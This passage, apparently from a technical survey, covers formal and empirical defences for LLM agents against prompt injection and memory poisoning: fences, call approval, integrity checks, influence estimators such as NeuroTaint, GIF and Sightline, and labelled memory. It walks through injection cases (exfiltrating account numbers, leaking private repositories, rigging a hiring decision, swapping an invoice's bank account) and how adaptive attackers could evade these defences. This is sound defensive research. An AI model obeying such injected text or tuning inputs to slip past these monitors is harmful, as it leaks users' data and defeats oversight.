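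A fence is a rule that takes tools away once the agent has read something untrusted. Suppose Alice's agent looks up her account number, reads an email and shows her a summary. The email contains an instruction to fetch a web address with the account number in it. The plan never fetches anything, so the reference agent, which ignores injected instructions, reveals nothing, and the injected fetch is a leak. With a fence, the monitor revokes the fetching tool when the agent reads the email, and denies the fetch if the model requests it.

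The fence theorem extends this to every plan. If the monitor revokes every tool that an injection can call, does so at the first untrusted read, and never grants any of those tools back, then the agent is relatively secure. The theorem has further conditions:

- Each injected instruction makes one tool call.
- The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance, so when it obeys cannot depend on the secrets or on the monitor's responses.
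- The attacker sees the content and order of the messages that arrive, but not their timing.
- The run ends. For an agent that runs for ever, the theorem also requires that the model does not go on obeying injections without end.

The proof compares the two agents step by step. Before the first untrusted read, neither agent has seen any injected instructions, so they take the same steps. Afterwards, whenever the model makes an injected call, the monitor silently denies it and the reference agent waits. All other steps match, and the monitor treats both agents identically, so the attacker sees the same messages from each. The same argument proves the uniform version.

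The first condition matters because an instruction that runs a small program can do harm without calling a tool. It can copy a secret into a variable that the plan is about to send, so the plan's own call leaks the secret. Dongol proves that a fence is still enough if such programs run in a sandbox that discards their changes, provided the fence covers reading as well as calling tools.

The condition on the schedule seems harder to meet. A model often has the secret and the attacker's text in the same context, so its decision to obey that text could well depend on both. Dongol leaves such models to future work.

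The theorem also assumes a harness in which every tool call and untrusted read passes through the monitor, a trusted program runs the plan, and a denied call has no effect that the attacker can see. An agent would violate these assumptions if it loaded an image from the attacker's server when showing the user a reply.

Revoking tools also prevents the agent from doing work that needs them. Dongol models a reported attack in which a user asks an agent to look at the open issues of a public GitHub repository. One issue contains an instruction to publish information from the user's private repositories in a pull request, a proposed change that anyone can read. Revoking the pull-request tool when the agent reads the first issue prevents the leak, but the agent then can't propose a fix for any of the issues.

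### Early, middle and late fences

Dongol also lets the plan raise the fence itself, with a command that locks the sending tool for the rest of the run. Where the plan puts this command determines what an injection can reach:

| Fence | Order of steps | What an injected message can reveal |
|---|---|---|
| Late | read email, read secret, lock | the secret |
| Middle | read email, lock, read secret | anything already in memory |
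| Early | lock, read email | nothing |

With the middle fence, the agent can still leak private data, even though it reads the secret only after the lock. The agent may have started with private data from an earlier session, and the model can send that data as soon as it has read the email. Only the early fence is secure for every injection that makes a single call.

Agents differ from processors in where the fence has to go. Derrick and colleagues advise programmers to put a processor's fence as late as possible, just before the instruction that would leak, because an early fence prevents useful guessing. An injection can add its own leaking instruction at any point after the model reads it, so an agent's fence has to be in place as soon as the model has read the injection.

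An agent that handles one request after another eventually needs its tools back. Restoring them while an old email is still in the model's context causes a leak, because the model may then obey that email. Dongol restores the tools only when a new session has cleared everything the model retains from untrusted text.

### Approving a tool and approving a call

Human approval lets an agent use a tool after it has read untrusted text. In one of Dongol's examples, an agent repeatedly reads an email, takes a reply that Alice has approved and sends it. If her approval covers the tool, it permits the next message whatever it contains. An attacker emails an instruction to send Alice's private data, and the model obeys after she approves her reply but before the plan sends it. Sending the data to the attacker uses up the approval, so the monitor blocks Alice's reply.

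A limit on the number of calls has the same weakness. If an agent is allowed to send only one message, an injection can make it send the attacker's message before the planned one. The limit helps only if the agent sends the planned message before it reads anything untrusted.

Approving the exact call works much better. The monitor then allows only the message that Alice saw, so an injected message gets through only if it is identical to that one. Provided the model doesn't obey injected instructions forever, every reply she approves eventually goes out and nothing else does.

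The attacker may still learn something from when the message arrives. Suppose Alice is negotiating a price, her private data is the most she will pay, and she approves an offer of $500. The injection tells the agent to send her maximum:

| Alice's maximum | Injected message | Planned message | What the attacker sees |
|---|---|---|---|
| $600 | denied | sent | "$500" at the usual step |
| $500 | sent | denied | "$500" one step early |

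The message is the same in both cases, but if it arrives early, it reveals that $500 is her limit. Dongol proves that call approval is secure against an attacker who sees only the content and order of messages, but leaks to one who also sees when each step happens. A real attacker may find it difficult to notice a one-step difference among ordinary delays. The harness could also prevent the leak by sending replies at fixed times.

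### Agents with two models

When a quarantined model reads the untrusted text, an injection can only change that model's answers, so Dongol lets the attacker choose those answers directly. In the examples from the discussion of CaMeL, an agent reads a user's private notes and an email, then replies to the sender.

The agent without labels leaks, and so does the labelled agent that branches on an answer. The other labelled agent is secure, but the monitor blocks every reply it tries to send. Its relative security therefore amounts to noninterference, and the reference agent does no useful work either.

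Even that conclusion depends on how much of a refusal the attacker can see. If an error message shows the blocked reply, the attacker can read the notes there, but nothing leaks if it shows only which tool the monitor refused.

### Machine-checked verdicts

Dongol's definitions and proofs take up about 31,600 lines in Isabelle/HOL, a proof assistant similar to Lean. They cover 25 example agents. Ten are secure, nine leak, and the security of the other six depends on what the attacker can see or how the model behaves. Claude Code helped generate the theorems and proofs, Isabelle checked every proof, and Dongol compared the paper's definitions and theorems with the formal versions.

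A machine can therefore check relative security, at least for an agent described in this formal language. When the agent leaks, the disproof also provides a concrete test, consisting of two secrets, one message from the attacker and the observation that distinguishes the secrets. A monitor can't check the property by watching a single run, because the definition compares several runs.

Eight of the ten "secure" verdicts cover only the attacks that Dongol wrote for each example, although the fence theorems extend two of them to whole classes of attack. The agents are tiny, with plans of a few steps, and Dongol presents them as tests of the definition, not as models of complete products.

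### Harm without a leak

Relative security concerns only leaks. If an injection makes the agent delete Alice's files, and the attacker learns nothing from the deletion, the agent is still relatively secure. The same is true if the agent pays the attacker $500, as long as the payment doesn't depend on her private data. Dongol calls this hijacking and excludes it. Many of AgentDojo's attacks have this form, so they could still succeed against a relatively secure agent.

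The comparison also requires that a reference agent exist. An ordinary agent chooses each tool call after reading the last result, so it has no plan for the reference agent to follow. FIDES works this way too. Its rule for consequential actions resembles a fence, but the theorem does not cover its full planning loop. Dongol also excludes tools whose replies depend on what the agent sends them, such as a search engine that the attacker runs.

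If the plan itself discloses too much, the reference agent does too, so the comparison won't show a problem. Dongol offers a partial remedy. If someone proves that the reference agent reveals at most the calendar, for example, then any relatively secure agent with that plan also reveals at most the calendar. But someone still has to decide that revealing the calendar is acceptable, which is part of the work of writing a release policy.

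A monitor that denies every call passes, since neither agent then sends anything. Utility needs a separate test.

Removing a tool can make a secure agent insecure. Suppose the plan sends the attacker a report by design, and an injection also makes the agent put the report in a web address and fetch it. The agent is secure because the injection gives the attacker nothing new. If an administrator revokes the sending tool, the reference agent no longer discloses the report. This makes the standard stricter, so the injected fetch becomes a leak even though the agent does less than before.

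The version that ignores timing can also miss an obvious leak, because it compares only runs in which the attacker receives the same number of messages between reads. Suppose an injection makes the agent request a permitted page if a secret is 0 and a forbidden page otherwise, and the plan then sends a completion message. The attacker receives two messages if the secret is 0 and one otherwise, and can therefore tell which case occurred, but this version never compares the two runs. The version with timing detects some such leaks, but neither version handles message counts in general.

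### Decisions that depend only on relevant content

Some attacks distort an agent's judgement without causing a leak or an unauthorised tool call. For example, a paper submitted for review might include a claim that leading experts regard it as the best work in its field, and an agent reviewing the paper might raise its score because of this. Qu, Xu and colleagues (2026) argue in *Securing LLM Agents Need Intent-to-Execution Integrity* that a definition of agent security should also cover such attacks.

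They combine four requirements. Each action must follow from an authenticated user's instruction, data must not reach places where it isn't allowed, tools must do only what they advertise, and irrelevant content must not change the agent's decisions. The last of these, judgment integrity, has a formula. Let *q* be the user's request, *d* the untrusted data, *J* the agent's decision and *δ* a change to the data:

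```
J(q, d with δ) = J(q, d)     for every task-irrelevant δ
```

A change is task-irrelevant if it doesn't alter the answer that a correct reasoner would give. Noninterference would require the equation to hold for every change, which would prevent the agent from reviewing the paper. Judgment integrity allows the paper's contribution to affect the score but doesn't allow its self-praise to do so.

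Deciding which changes are irrelevant is difficult because it requires knowing the correct answer, which is usually what the user wants the agent to find. The formula also doesn't protect against lies. If a stranger adds a needed file to a list of old drafts, the correct answer to "Which drafts does this list name?" changes, so judgment integrity doesn't stop the agent from naming the file.

An automated test can find violations of judgment integrity one at a time by adding a sentence of praise and checking whether the score changes. It can't confirm that there are no violations, because there are too many possible edits to try. Qu and colleagues accept that no current technique can guarantee judgment integrity. They defend the definition as a target, just as a formal definition of a correct program is useful even when nobody can yet verify a large program.

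*AgentSecBench* (Alpay and Alpay, 2026) has a similar limit in testing a property that compares how often a forbidden outcome occurs with and without an attacker's text, while holding fixed the information that the agent may use. Its tests plant a recognisable marker in the data and look for it in the output. Finding the marker shows that the agent is insecure, but the tests can't certify the property because the agent could paraphrase the secret without reproducing the marker.

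Qu and colleagues also rate existing defences. They rate CaMeL as fully protecting instructions and data flow, but not protecting judgement or tools at all. The rating for data flow seems too high, given the leak that Garby and colleagues found in CaMeL's labels. But CaMeL does leave judgement unprotected, because fixing the plan doesn't prevent flattery from influencing a score. The lack of protection for tools also matters, because both CaMeL and relative security depend on the tools being trustworthy. Qu and colleagues cite an audit of 42,447 add-on skills for agents, which found at least one vulnerability in 26.1% of them.

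Relative security extends *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (Siu, He and colleagues, 2026), in which the security of an action depends on who asked for it and why. For example, an instruction to delete a file is legitimate if it comes from the user but an attack if it comes from a web page. To judge security from a single run, the framework assumes idealised functions, including one that identifies which instruction the agent followed. Siu and colleagues acknowledge that perfect versions of these functions may not exist. Relative security does not need them because it compares the agent with one that never obeys untrusted text.

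### Authority for each part of an action

*Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) sets a more modest requirement that a harness can check. Untrusted text may influence what the model proposes, but each important part of a proposed action needs its own authority before the harness carries out the action.

Suppose a coding agent reads the log of a failed test. The log can properly identify the file that failed, but it shouldn't choose which tool to run or mark a change as approved. The rule for a protected field, such as a file path or a recipient, is:

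```
untrusted text  →  protected field           forbidden
untrusted text  →  typed release  →  field   allowed
```

A typed release is a value that trusted code has checked and approved for one field only, which makes it a narrow form of endorsement. The file path from the log may fill the `file_path` field, but the harness would reject it if it were used as a tool name.

Valid fields aren't enough: if the agent proposes a patch, trusted code must also authorise the exact change that the patch would make to the repository. The call also needs a single-use permission, so that an attacker can't cause a legitimate action to run twice. The harness ties all these authorisations to one record of the proposed action, uses up the permission and then runs the action. If anything changes after the check, the record no longer matches and the harness refuses to run the action.

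Fixed code can check this property before every call. The check works only if the policies, validators and records of what influenced each field are correct, and if every route to a side effect passes through it. Santos-Grueiro doesn't claim noninterference for the model itself, and a harness using a hosted model can't inspect how the provider computed the reply.

Coding agents completed the task safely in 231 of 400 trials, and no action ran without the required authority. In 73 of the other trials, the harness could not parse the agent's output. In 61, the proposed change never received authorisation, and in 35, the agent carried out an authorised action but failed the task. The absence of unauthorised actions shows that the gate enforced its policies. It can't show that the policies were right, because an action counted as unauthorised only if it lacked the authority those policies required.

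Getting the policies right takes work. An audit of 24 types of action and their 149 fields initially found 18 problems, including approvals in free text and releases that were valid in too many places. When Santos-Grueiro regenerated the audit, it listed nine high-severity and nine medium-severity findings, but none that in the end blocked the policies under test. Other developers would have to repeat this work for their own tools.

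A correct release can still let a stranger choose among permitted values. If the policy for deleting drafts accepts any file path inside Ana's project, `plan-b.md` is as valid as the path of a real draft. The harness can verify that the path is well formed and in the right folder, and that Ana authorised a deletion. Whether she wanted to delete that particular file is a question of judgement. Santos-Grueiro's check leaves that question open, and Qu and colleagues' definition covers it only if someone already knows the answer.

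## Estimating which inputs influenced a model's output

Santos-Grueiro's check depends on a record of what influenced each field of a proposed action. A harness can record this for its own code, but it has access only to a hosted model's input and output text. It therefore has to treat everything in the context as having influenced the reply, as FIDES does when it joins the labels. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* accepts the same rule for now but warns that it leads to "label explosion", in which every piece of data ends up with every label.

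Inspecting a model's reply isn't enough to determine which inputs influenced it. Suppose a user asks what is on for Friday, and the context contains a calendar and a newsletter. The model answers "Dentist at 3 pm." None of those words come from the newsletter, but the calendar may also list a lunch that the newsletter told the model to leave out. Ruling out influence would require showing that the model would give the same answer whatever the newsletter contained, and the harness has run the model with only one version.

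Models ignore some of what they read. *Sightline* (Xu, Li and colleagues, 2026) studied calls to language models in code from 2,103 groups of related open-source repositories and found that between 12% and 14% of the inputs did not reach the output. This share matters because a single unused input from a stranger is enough to make a reply untrusted. If a harness could identify such inputs, an agent that had opened a stranger's email and ignored it could still make a payment.

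### Regenerating the answer from fewer inputs

One approach is to find the inputs that mattered and then ask the model again without the others. Siddiqui, Gaonkar and colleagues (2025), in *Permissive Information-Flow Analysis for Large Language Models*, developed this method. In outline:

```
draft  = model(all messages)
keep   = the messages that appear to have influenced draft
answer = model(keep)
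label(answer) = join of the labels of the messages in keep
```

The second call reduces the harm from mistakes in the analysis. If the analysis wrongly decides that the newsletter had no influence, the model answers again from the calendar alone, and the lunch reappears in the answer. If the analysis drops a message the model needed, the answer gets worse, but its label still covers everything the model read to write it.

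One remaining route for influence is the choice of messages, which depends on all of them. Suppose the context holds an old calendar and a new one, and something in the newsletter leads the analysis to keep only the old one. The answer consists entirely of trusted text, but the newsletter determined which text, an implicit flow that the label doesn't record. With ten messages there are 2^10, or 1,024, possible selections, so this flow can carry at most 10 bits per answer.

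In an agent setting, Siddiqui and colleagues obtained a less restrictive label than their baseline in more than 85% of cases. The baseline predicted the label by introspection, so this figure doesn't measure how often the method improves on a full join, or how many blocked actions it would allow. Costa and colleagues describe the regenerated answers as comparable in usefulness to the originals. They designed FIDES to accommodate the method but left it out for simplicity.

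The other three methods estimate influence without regenerating the output. If an estimate wrongly rules out an input's influence, the original output stays in use with a label that is too permissive.

### NeuroTaint: reconstructing flows from a log

*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and colleagues, April 2026) introduced NeuroTaint, which audits an agent's log after the run. It can report that a stranger's text led to an email, but only after the harness has sent it.

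From the log, NeuroTaint builds a graph of tool calls that records where each piece of data came from. For every sink, it then looks for text from the untrusted sources that could have reached it. It applies four tests, starting with the cheapest:

1. It checks for a unique marker that it attached to the source's text when the tool returned it.
2. It measures how much of the text the source and the sink share in the same order, and reports a flow if this is at least 15% of the shorter text.
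3. It compares embeddings, lists of numbers that represent meaning, to catch paraphrases.
4. It repeats that comparison on small chunks of the source, since one malicious sentence barely affects the embedding of a long web page.

These tests can't find implicit flows. For example, an email announcing a "new policy" may cause an agent to forward a customer's message that contains none of the policy's text. If none of the four tests detects a flow, NeuroTaint replaces the source with a neutral placeholder, such as "No relevant information found", and has a language model judge whether the agent would still have made the same call. NeuroTaint treats a "no" as evidence of influence.

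This question closely follows the definition of influence, but a model predicts the answer without rerunning the agent. NeuroTaint also replaces sources one at a time. If two emails contain the same instruction, removing either one alone changes nothing, so the test can miss the influence of both. Xu and colleagues prove that any method based on removing a single input has this weakness.

### The NeuroTaint benchmark

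Cai and colleagues also built the benchmark on which they tested NeuroTaint. TaintBench has 400 scenarios in 20 agent frameworks, half with a flow from an untrusted source to a sink and half without. They compared NeuroTaint with a baseline modelled on FIDES, using GPT-4.1-mini as the agent and taking a majority vote over five runs. The table groups some of their categories:

| Scenario | Cases | Flagged by NeuroTaint | Flagged by baseline |
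|---|---|---|---|
| Flow: text copied whole or in fragments | 75 | 75 | 51 |
| Flow: text rewritten over several steps | 42 | 35 | 31 |
| Flow: source affects the choice of action | 40 | 37 | 17 |
| Flow: across sessions or agents | 30 | 28 | 5 |
| Flow: other | 13 | 12 | 4 |
| No flow: source and sink both appear | 140 | 1 | 94 |
| No flow: clean scenario | 40 | 0 | 0 |
| No flow: source and sink share a topic | 14 | 14 | 9 |
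| No flow: model could know the content already | 6 | 1 | 3 |

NeuroTaint found 37 of the 40 implicit flows, while the baseline found 17. In the main group of 140 scenarios without a flow, NeuroTaint raised one false alarm and the baseline raised 94. But NeuroTaint wrongly flagged all 14 scenarios in which the source and the sink merely shared a topic. In the 20 scenarios designed to look most like flows, it raised 15 false alarms and the baseline raised 12. NeuroTaint seems to have trouble distinguishing a shared topic from a shared origin. Shim and colleagues raise a different objection to comparing embeddings, which is that similarity doesn't track leakage when outputs are short or restructured.

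The baseline is also a poor stand-in for FIDES. It treats a known path from a source to a sink as strong evidence of a flow, whereas FIDES's basic loop joins the labels of everything in the context. If the untrusted text was in the context with the right label, that loop would mark every implicit flow, but it would also raise many false alarms. In four of the 20 frameworks, the baseline flagged nothing, which suggests that it didn't recognise their tools. In the other 16, it flagged 108 of 160 scenarios with a flow and 106 of 160 without one, so it barely distinguished them.

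TaintBench labels each scenario by the flow it was designed to produce, whether or not the agent produced it. When Cai and colleagues used Claude Opus 4.6 as the agent, NeuroTaint flagged only 54.7% of the scenarios designed to produce a flow, probably in part because the agent often refused to act on the attack. On InjecAgent, an existing benchmark from another group, NeuroTaint and the baseline both scored above 99% on a measure that combines missed cases and false alarms. InjecAgent labels unsafe actions rather than flows, so it doesn't test NeuroTaint's main advantage, and TaintBench is the only evidence for that advantage.

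### Graded labels

The methods so far record whether an input influenced the output, but not how much. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* proposes giving each output soft labels, which would estimate how much information the output contains about each labelled input. An answer about Friday might have a high value for the calendar and a value near zero for the newsletter. The paper also suggests removing or changing inputs to measure their effect on the agent's actions, and examining the model's internals to find a simpler algorithm that behaves like the model and that a harness could track.

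Graded labels draw on quantitative information flow, which treats a computation as a channel with a capacity for carrying information. *Reachability Across the NL/PL Boundary* (2026) places language model calls on a range from a channel with zero capacity, which always returns the same output, to one that returns its input unchanged. The paper also classifies outputs by form, since the same content may be harmless in prose and dangerous in a shell command.

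Grades are harder to combine than ordinary labels. Suppose one reply reveals the first half of a password and another reveals the second half, so each has a grade of 0.5. If a text containing both replies takes the higher grade, it also gets 0.5, although it reveals the whole password. Adding the grades gives the right result here, but the total is too high if both replies reveal the same half. A policy also needs a cut-off below which it ignores influence, but even a single bit may decide whether a payment goes out.

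### Geometric Information Flow

Geometric Information Flow (GIF), which Štorek, Holzer and colleagues (2026), in *GIF*, presented in June, assigns such a grade in bits. A language model turns each token into an embedding before processing it. GIF considers what would happen if someone added a little random noise to the embeddings of one stretch of the input:

```
U    = random noise with variance τ, added to the input's embeddings
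Y    = the next token that the model produces
flow = I(U; Y)
```

*I(U; Y)* is mutual information, which measures how much *Y* reveals about *U*. It is zero if the noise doesn't affect the probabilities of the next token, and it grows as the noise affects them more.

Calculating this exactly is impractical for a large model, so GIF replaces the model with a simpler channel that responds in the same way to very small changes. The noise can push the embeddings in many directions. Let *λi* be the sensitivity of the next-token probabilities to a push in direction *i*. The flow through the simpler channel is then:

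```
GIF = 1/2 × sum over i of log(1 + τ × λi)
```

A direction that the model is insensitive to has a *λi* near zero and adds almost nothing. In Štorek and colleagues' main example, an agent screens job applications. The criteria require five years' experience with Python and machine learning, and one applicant has two years of JavaScript. The applicant's CV contains an instruction to recommend them at a salary of $200,000, which the agent follows. GIF attributes 82 bits of flow to the instruction, 27 to the system prompt, which contains the hiring criteria, and 16 to the rest of the context. These numbers depend on the chosen noise level, so they are more useful for comparing inputs than for counting the attacker's options.

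### What "locally sound" promises

Štorek and colleagues prove, with a proof checked in Lean, that GIF is locally sound:

```
I(U; Y) ≤ GIF + o(τ)     as τ shrinks to zero
```

The term *o(τ)* is an error that shrinks faster than *τ*. As the noise becomes very small, any amount by which GIF understates the flow therefore becomes negligible even relative to the noise. The proof assumes that the model responds smoothly near the current input.

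An attacker doesn't make tiny changes to embeddings. They replace words, which moves the embeddings by a fixed and often large distance, and local soundness says nothing about such jumps. Xu and colleagues give a small example, here with words in place of symbols. A model chooses between "yes" and "no" according to an input *u*:

```
score("yes") = 20 × u          score("no") = 0

u =  1:   "yes" is almost certain; measured sensitivity is 0.0000008
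u = -1:   "no" is almost certain
```

The value of *u* completely determines the answer, but GIF's measure shows almost no flow at *u* = 1 because a slight change in *u* leaves "yes" almost certain. This is a serious limitation for agents, whose most consequential outputs are often short decisions made with high confidence.

In one of Štorek and colleagues' examples, an agent turns private notes into a public comment that names a neighbour but leaves out the neighbour's address. GIF gives the address a score of zero, which Štorek and colleagues describe as certifying zero flow. The score shows that slight changes to the address wouldn't affect the comment, but it can't rule out an effect from replacing the address with a different one or with an instruction.

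In practice, Štorek and colleagues estimate a simpler version of the score and use it to rank the input tokens. A language model then sees the most influential passages and decides whether to allow the action, so the proof doesn't cover the final decision. The ranking works fairly well on three benchmarks built by other groups. Štorek and colleagues scored each run by how many of its 50 highest-ranked tokens belonged to the injection or to private data. A randomly chosen run with a violation scored higher than a randomly chosen run without one 91% of the time on AgentDojo and 92% on MSB, which both test prompt injection, and 75% on AgentDAM, which tests privacy leaks in web browsing. Chance would be 50%. With only the highlighted passages, models judged actions between 0.97 and 1.22 times as well as they did with the complete record, and on the two injection benchmarks they needed as little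 as about a third of the tokens.

### Sightline: separating what a model reads from what it uses

Sightline, released in November, relies on attention, the mechanism that most language models use to move information between tokens. For each new token, each of the model's attention heads (Qwen3-8B has 1,152) divides its weight among the tokens so far. Xu and colleagues call the weight on an input the "reading" of that input.

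If no chain of attention leads from an input to the output, a slight change to that input provably has no effect on the output. This theorem rarely rules out an input's influence in practice, because attention gives every input at least a little weight. The size of the weight doesn't determine whether an input mattered either. An attention head can give an input a large weight and contribute nothing to the output, or give it a weight of two billionths when a different value of the same input would have changed the answer.

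Sightline therefore learns from examples which readings matter. For each input, it records every head's average and highest reading, along with the input's share of what that head reads from the prompt. This gives 3,456 numbers per input with Qwen3-8B. A simple statistical model trained on labelled calls combines these numbers into a score, and a low score suggests that the input was not used.

The threshold for dropping a label comes from a procedure called conformal calibration. Suppose the developers want to miss at most 1% of real flows and have labelled calls from 999 groups of repositories:

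1. They pick one real flow at random from each group and compute its score.
2. They sort the 999 scores and set the threshold at the tenth lowest.
3. From then on, Sightline drops an input's label if its score is below the threshold.

If the next real flow comes from the same kind of source as the others, it is equally likely to take any of the 1,000 places in the combined ranking. Sightline misses it only if it lands in one of the lowest ten places, so the chance of a miss is at most 10 in 1,000, or 1%. This bound holds however good the scores are, but poor scores push the threshold so low that Sightline can remove few labels.

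Xu and colleagues assembled the main test set themselves from open-source code and used a language model to fill in plausible input values. Three other language models judged which inputs each output used. At the 1% setting, Sightline removed between 43.9% and 65.6% of the unnecessary labels, depending on the model, and missed about 1% of real flows. The miss rate stayed close to 1% when they calibrated Sightline on a different collection of code.

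Sightline can also use an open model to read another model's recorded calls, which is useful for hosted models whose attention is not accessible. Across 12 pairings of open models, this was about as accurate as using each model to read its own calls.

### Half the label creep

To test Sightline on agents, Xu and colleagues recorded a Qwen3-8B agent under attack in AgentDojo, took 120 of its turns from 106 episodes and recalibrated Sightline to miss at most 5% of flows. It missed 3.9% and removed 50.0% of the label creep, meaning the labels that a full join would add from inputs the agent hadn't used. The best of the seven other methods removed 38.3%, and none of the rest, including GIF, removed more than 15.7%. Štorek and colleagues had found GIF better than attention, but the two tests measure different things, and each group ran its own version of the competing methods.

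Removing half of the unnecessary labels can unblock fewer than half of the blocked actions, because an action stays blocked until all of its untrusted labels are gone. If the context contains three unused, untrusted inputs and Sightline drops each label with an independent probability of one half, it unblocks the action only one time in eight. Xu and colleagues measured labels, not completed tasks, so the gain in utility is unknown.

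A FIDES-style policy applied to the resulting labels blocked all 34 tool calls that carried out an attack. This is encouraging, but the sample is small. If Sightline had an independent 8% chance of missing each such call, it would still catch all 34 about 6% of the time.

### What a miss rate means over many episodes

It is easy to read the 3.9% as the share of episodes in which Sightline misses something. The calibration picks one real flow from each episode, so the figure is closer to the chance of missing a randomly chosen flow from a randomly chosen episode. An episode with several flows has several chances to go wrong. If misses were independent, the chance of missing at least one flow would be:

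```
1 flow:                                 1 - 0.961      =   3.9%
5 flows in one episode:                 1 - 0.961^5    =  18.0%
10 episodes with one flow each:         1 - 0.961^10   =  32.8%
100 episodes with one flow each:        1 - 0.961^100  =  98.1%
```

A company that ran 1,000 such episodes a day could expect Sightline to miss about 39 flows a day. Most would be harmless, because most flows aren't attacks. If one episode in 1,000 contained an attack and Sightline missed attacks as often as other flows, about one attack would get past the labels every 26 days.

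The rate also counts only flows that are visible in the output. Xu and colleagues count an input as reaching the output if the output reflects the input's content or a decision that the content determined. If the newsletter had made the model leave out the lunch, the judges might well have recorded no flow.

### When an adversary chooses the input

The estimate of one attack every 26 days assumes that attacks resemble the flows in the calibration data. An attacker has every reason to make theirs different. The two kinds of guarantee are:

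```
statistical:   for a flow drawn at random from familiar use,
               the chance of a miss is at most 5%

worst case:    for every input that anyone could write,
               the method misses no flow
```

A miss rate of 3.9% may mean that every flow has a small chance of being missed, or that the same 3.9% of flows are missed every time. In the second case, an attacker only has to find one of those flows. If each new wording had an independent 3.9% chance of being missed, finding one that works would take about 26 attempts on average. When Sightline uses an open model to read the calls, an attacker who has the same model and the trained scoring rule can run that search in private. They can then send the successful wording to 1,000 agents and get past the labels in most or all of them.

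More calibration data doesn't remove this problem, because the guarantee holds only on average and an attacker can pick the cases where it fails. Xu and colleagues acknowledge the assumption. Their agent test used AgentDojo's attacks, which weren't written to evade Sightline. The adaptive attacks that Narisetty and colleagues describe broke most of the twelve earlier defences they targeted. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* conjectures that persistent attackers will always evade defences that rely on a model to separate instructions from data. Influence estimates could be equally fragile, since an attacker can optimise text against a score just as they can against a filter.

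None of the four methods fully solves the problem. NeuroTaint has no bound on its misses, and the judge it uses to assess causation may read the attacker's text. GIF's theorem covers every sufficiently small change around one input, but not the rewording an attacker would use. Sightline's theorem about attention covers slight changes to any input, but it allows a label to be removed only when no attention connects the input to the output.

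Siddiqui and colleagues' method comes closest to isolating influence, because text that the model doesn't read in the second call can't affect the answer directly. An attacker can still try to influence which messages the analysis keeps. A harness can prevent this by choosing messages by their labels alone. But FIDES already does this without estimating influence when it hides an untrusted result in a variable.

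## Memory and messages between agents

Storing untrusted text in a variable hides it from the planner during one task. But many agents keep notes, files and user profiles between tasks, and the harness later puts some of that material back into the model's context. Agents also pass their results to other agents. Either practice can expose a planner to the hidden text.

### From Monday's note to Tuesday's payment

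The model keeps nothing between calls, so any influence that lasts from one session to the next has to pass through something stored outside it. *Six misconceptions about large language models* (2026) lists logs, profiles, documents and search indices as the usual places.

Girrens and Wang give an example with two sessions. On Monday, a user asks an agent to fetch an invoice from a supplier called Acme and keep the details. An attacker has put their own bank account on the invoice. On Tuesday, the user asks the agent to pay the invoice they discussed yesterday. *MemoryDojo* (2026), a benchmark for poisoned memory, has a notation for such cases. Simplified, with *M* for the model and *H* for the harness as before, it gives:

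```
Monday:    memory  = write(old memory, everything that happened on Monday)

Tuesday:   context = request + retrieve(memory, request)
           action  = H(M(context))
```

If only the account number on Monday's invoice changes, the memory changes, so Tuesday's context changes, and the harness may pay a different account. Deleting the note on Monday night would stop the attack, but replacing the model with a fresh copy wouldn't, because *M* is the same function on both days.

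An attack through memory can take effect long after the attacker has gone. In *MemoryDojo*, the attacker adds text once, to something the agent reads in an earlier session, and can't alter later requests or tool results. *Hidden in Memory* (2026) showed that text from outside could lead ChatGPT, Claude and Gemini to store false memories that affected later sessions.

### SPA: stored results that keep their labels

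SPA, which Girrens and Wang published in August 2026, lets a later plan use a stored result that the planner hasn't read. The planner runs once per request and writes a complete plan in a small language. A plan can retrieve a stored result, call a tool, query a quarantined model, show something to the user, branch or loop.

After a successful run, the harness stores each result's value, its label and a description. The description gives the result's format, the request that produced it, and the planner's own note of what the result is for. On Tuesday, the planner sees the description but not the value, and might write a plan like this:

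```
retrieve    Monday's invoice  →  invoice
call tool   send_money(to = invoice.account, amount = invoice.amount)
```

A checker examines the plan before any of it runs. It gives `invoice` the untrusted label it had on Monday and compares that label with the policy for `send_money`. It also labels each step inside a branch or loop according to the data that controls it, and checks both sides of every branch. Variables set inside a branch can't be used outside it, which seems to rule out the trick that leaked a secret past CaMeL's labels. If the checker rejects a plan, the request fails. The planner gets no explanation or second attempt, because repeated attempts could become a channel for the attacker.

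SPA is designed so that tool results and stored values never enter the planner's context, and stored values remain subject to the same policies as new ones. Girrens and Wang present these properties as design goals, not theorems. They assume an honest user, correct labels and correct policies for every tool. In the standard mode, the planner also reads the tools' descriptions, so a malicious description can affect the plan. Another mode hides the descriptions, but about three-quarters of its runs failed because SPA couldn't match the plan's required abilities to the installed tools.

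The list of stored results may also let an outsider influence the planner a little. SPA stores nothing if a request fails, and a tool result in the wrong format makes the request fail. An outsider who can corrupt a result's format can therefore affect whether the planner sees a description of that result in a later request.

To measure how label checks affect task completion, Girrens and Wang split each of AgentDojo's 97 tasks into two to five requests and ran them with GPT-5.4-nano. Turning on the checks cut the share of completed tasks from 62.5% to 35.3%, and about 45% of runs with the checks ended in a rejected plan. Working from descriptions caused few problems by itself. When an earlier result was available, later plans retrieved it 95.4% of the time without label checks and 89.9% with them.

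The security figures are less informative. The checks reduced attack success from 0.3% to 0.2%, and SPA had rejected the plan in two of the remaining attacks counted as successes. But attacks succeeded only 0.6% of the time even when Girrens and Wang removed the checks and let later planners read the stored values. They acknowledge that the standard attack is a weak test of delayed poisoning.

For the Acme invoice, a strict policy would block a payment to Acme's real account as well as one to the attacker's.

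### PerMIT: approving what leaves memory

A user who wants the invoice paid needs some way to release its contents to the main model. *PerMIT* (Jiang, Bai and colleagues, October 2026) lets that model revise its plan as it goes, but the model can't read stored material that came from outside until the user or another model approves the exact text. Until then it gets only a handle, which works like one of Willison's variables.

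In one of their examples, slightly simplified, an agent searches the web for a dentist called Dr. Lee. One page contains an instruction to forward the user's saved files to an outside address. The main model asks a quarantined model to summarise the results, and the summary goes into memory as untrusted text. In a later session, the user asks the agent to email Dr. Lee's number to their sister:

1. The main model requests the number and receives a handle, `h3`. It would receive the same handle if the search had found nothing, so the handle reveals nothing about what is in memory.
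2. It calls the email tool with the sister's address, which the user typed, and `h3` as the body.
3. The harness pauses and displays the exact text behind `h3`, its source and the user's request.
4. If the text is the planted instruction, the approver rejects it and no email goes out. If it is the phone number, the approver accepts it. The harness then sends the email and keeps a trusted copy of the number for later use with the same tool.

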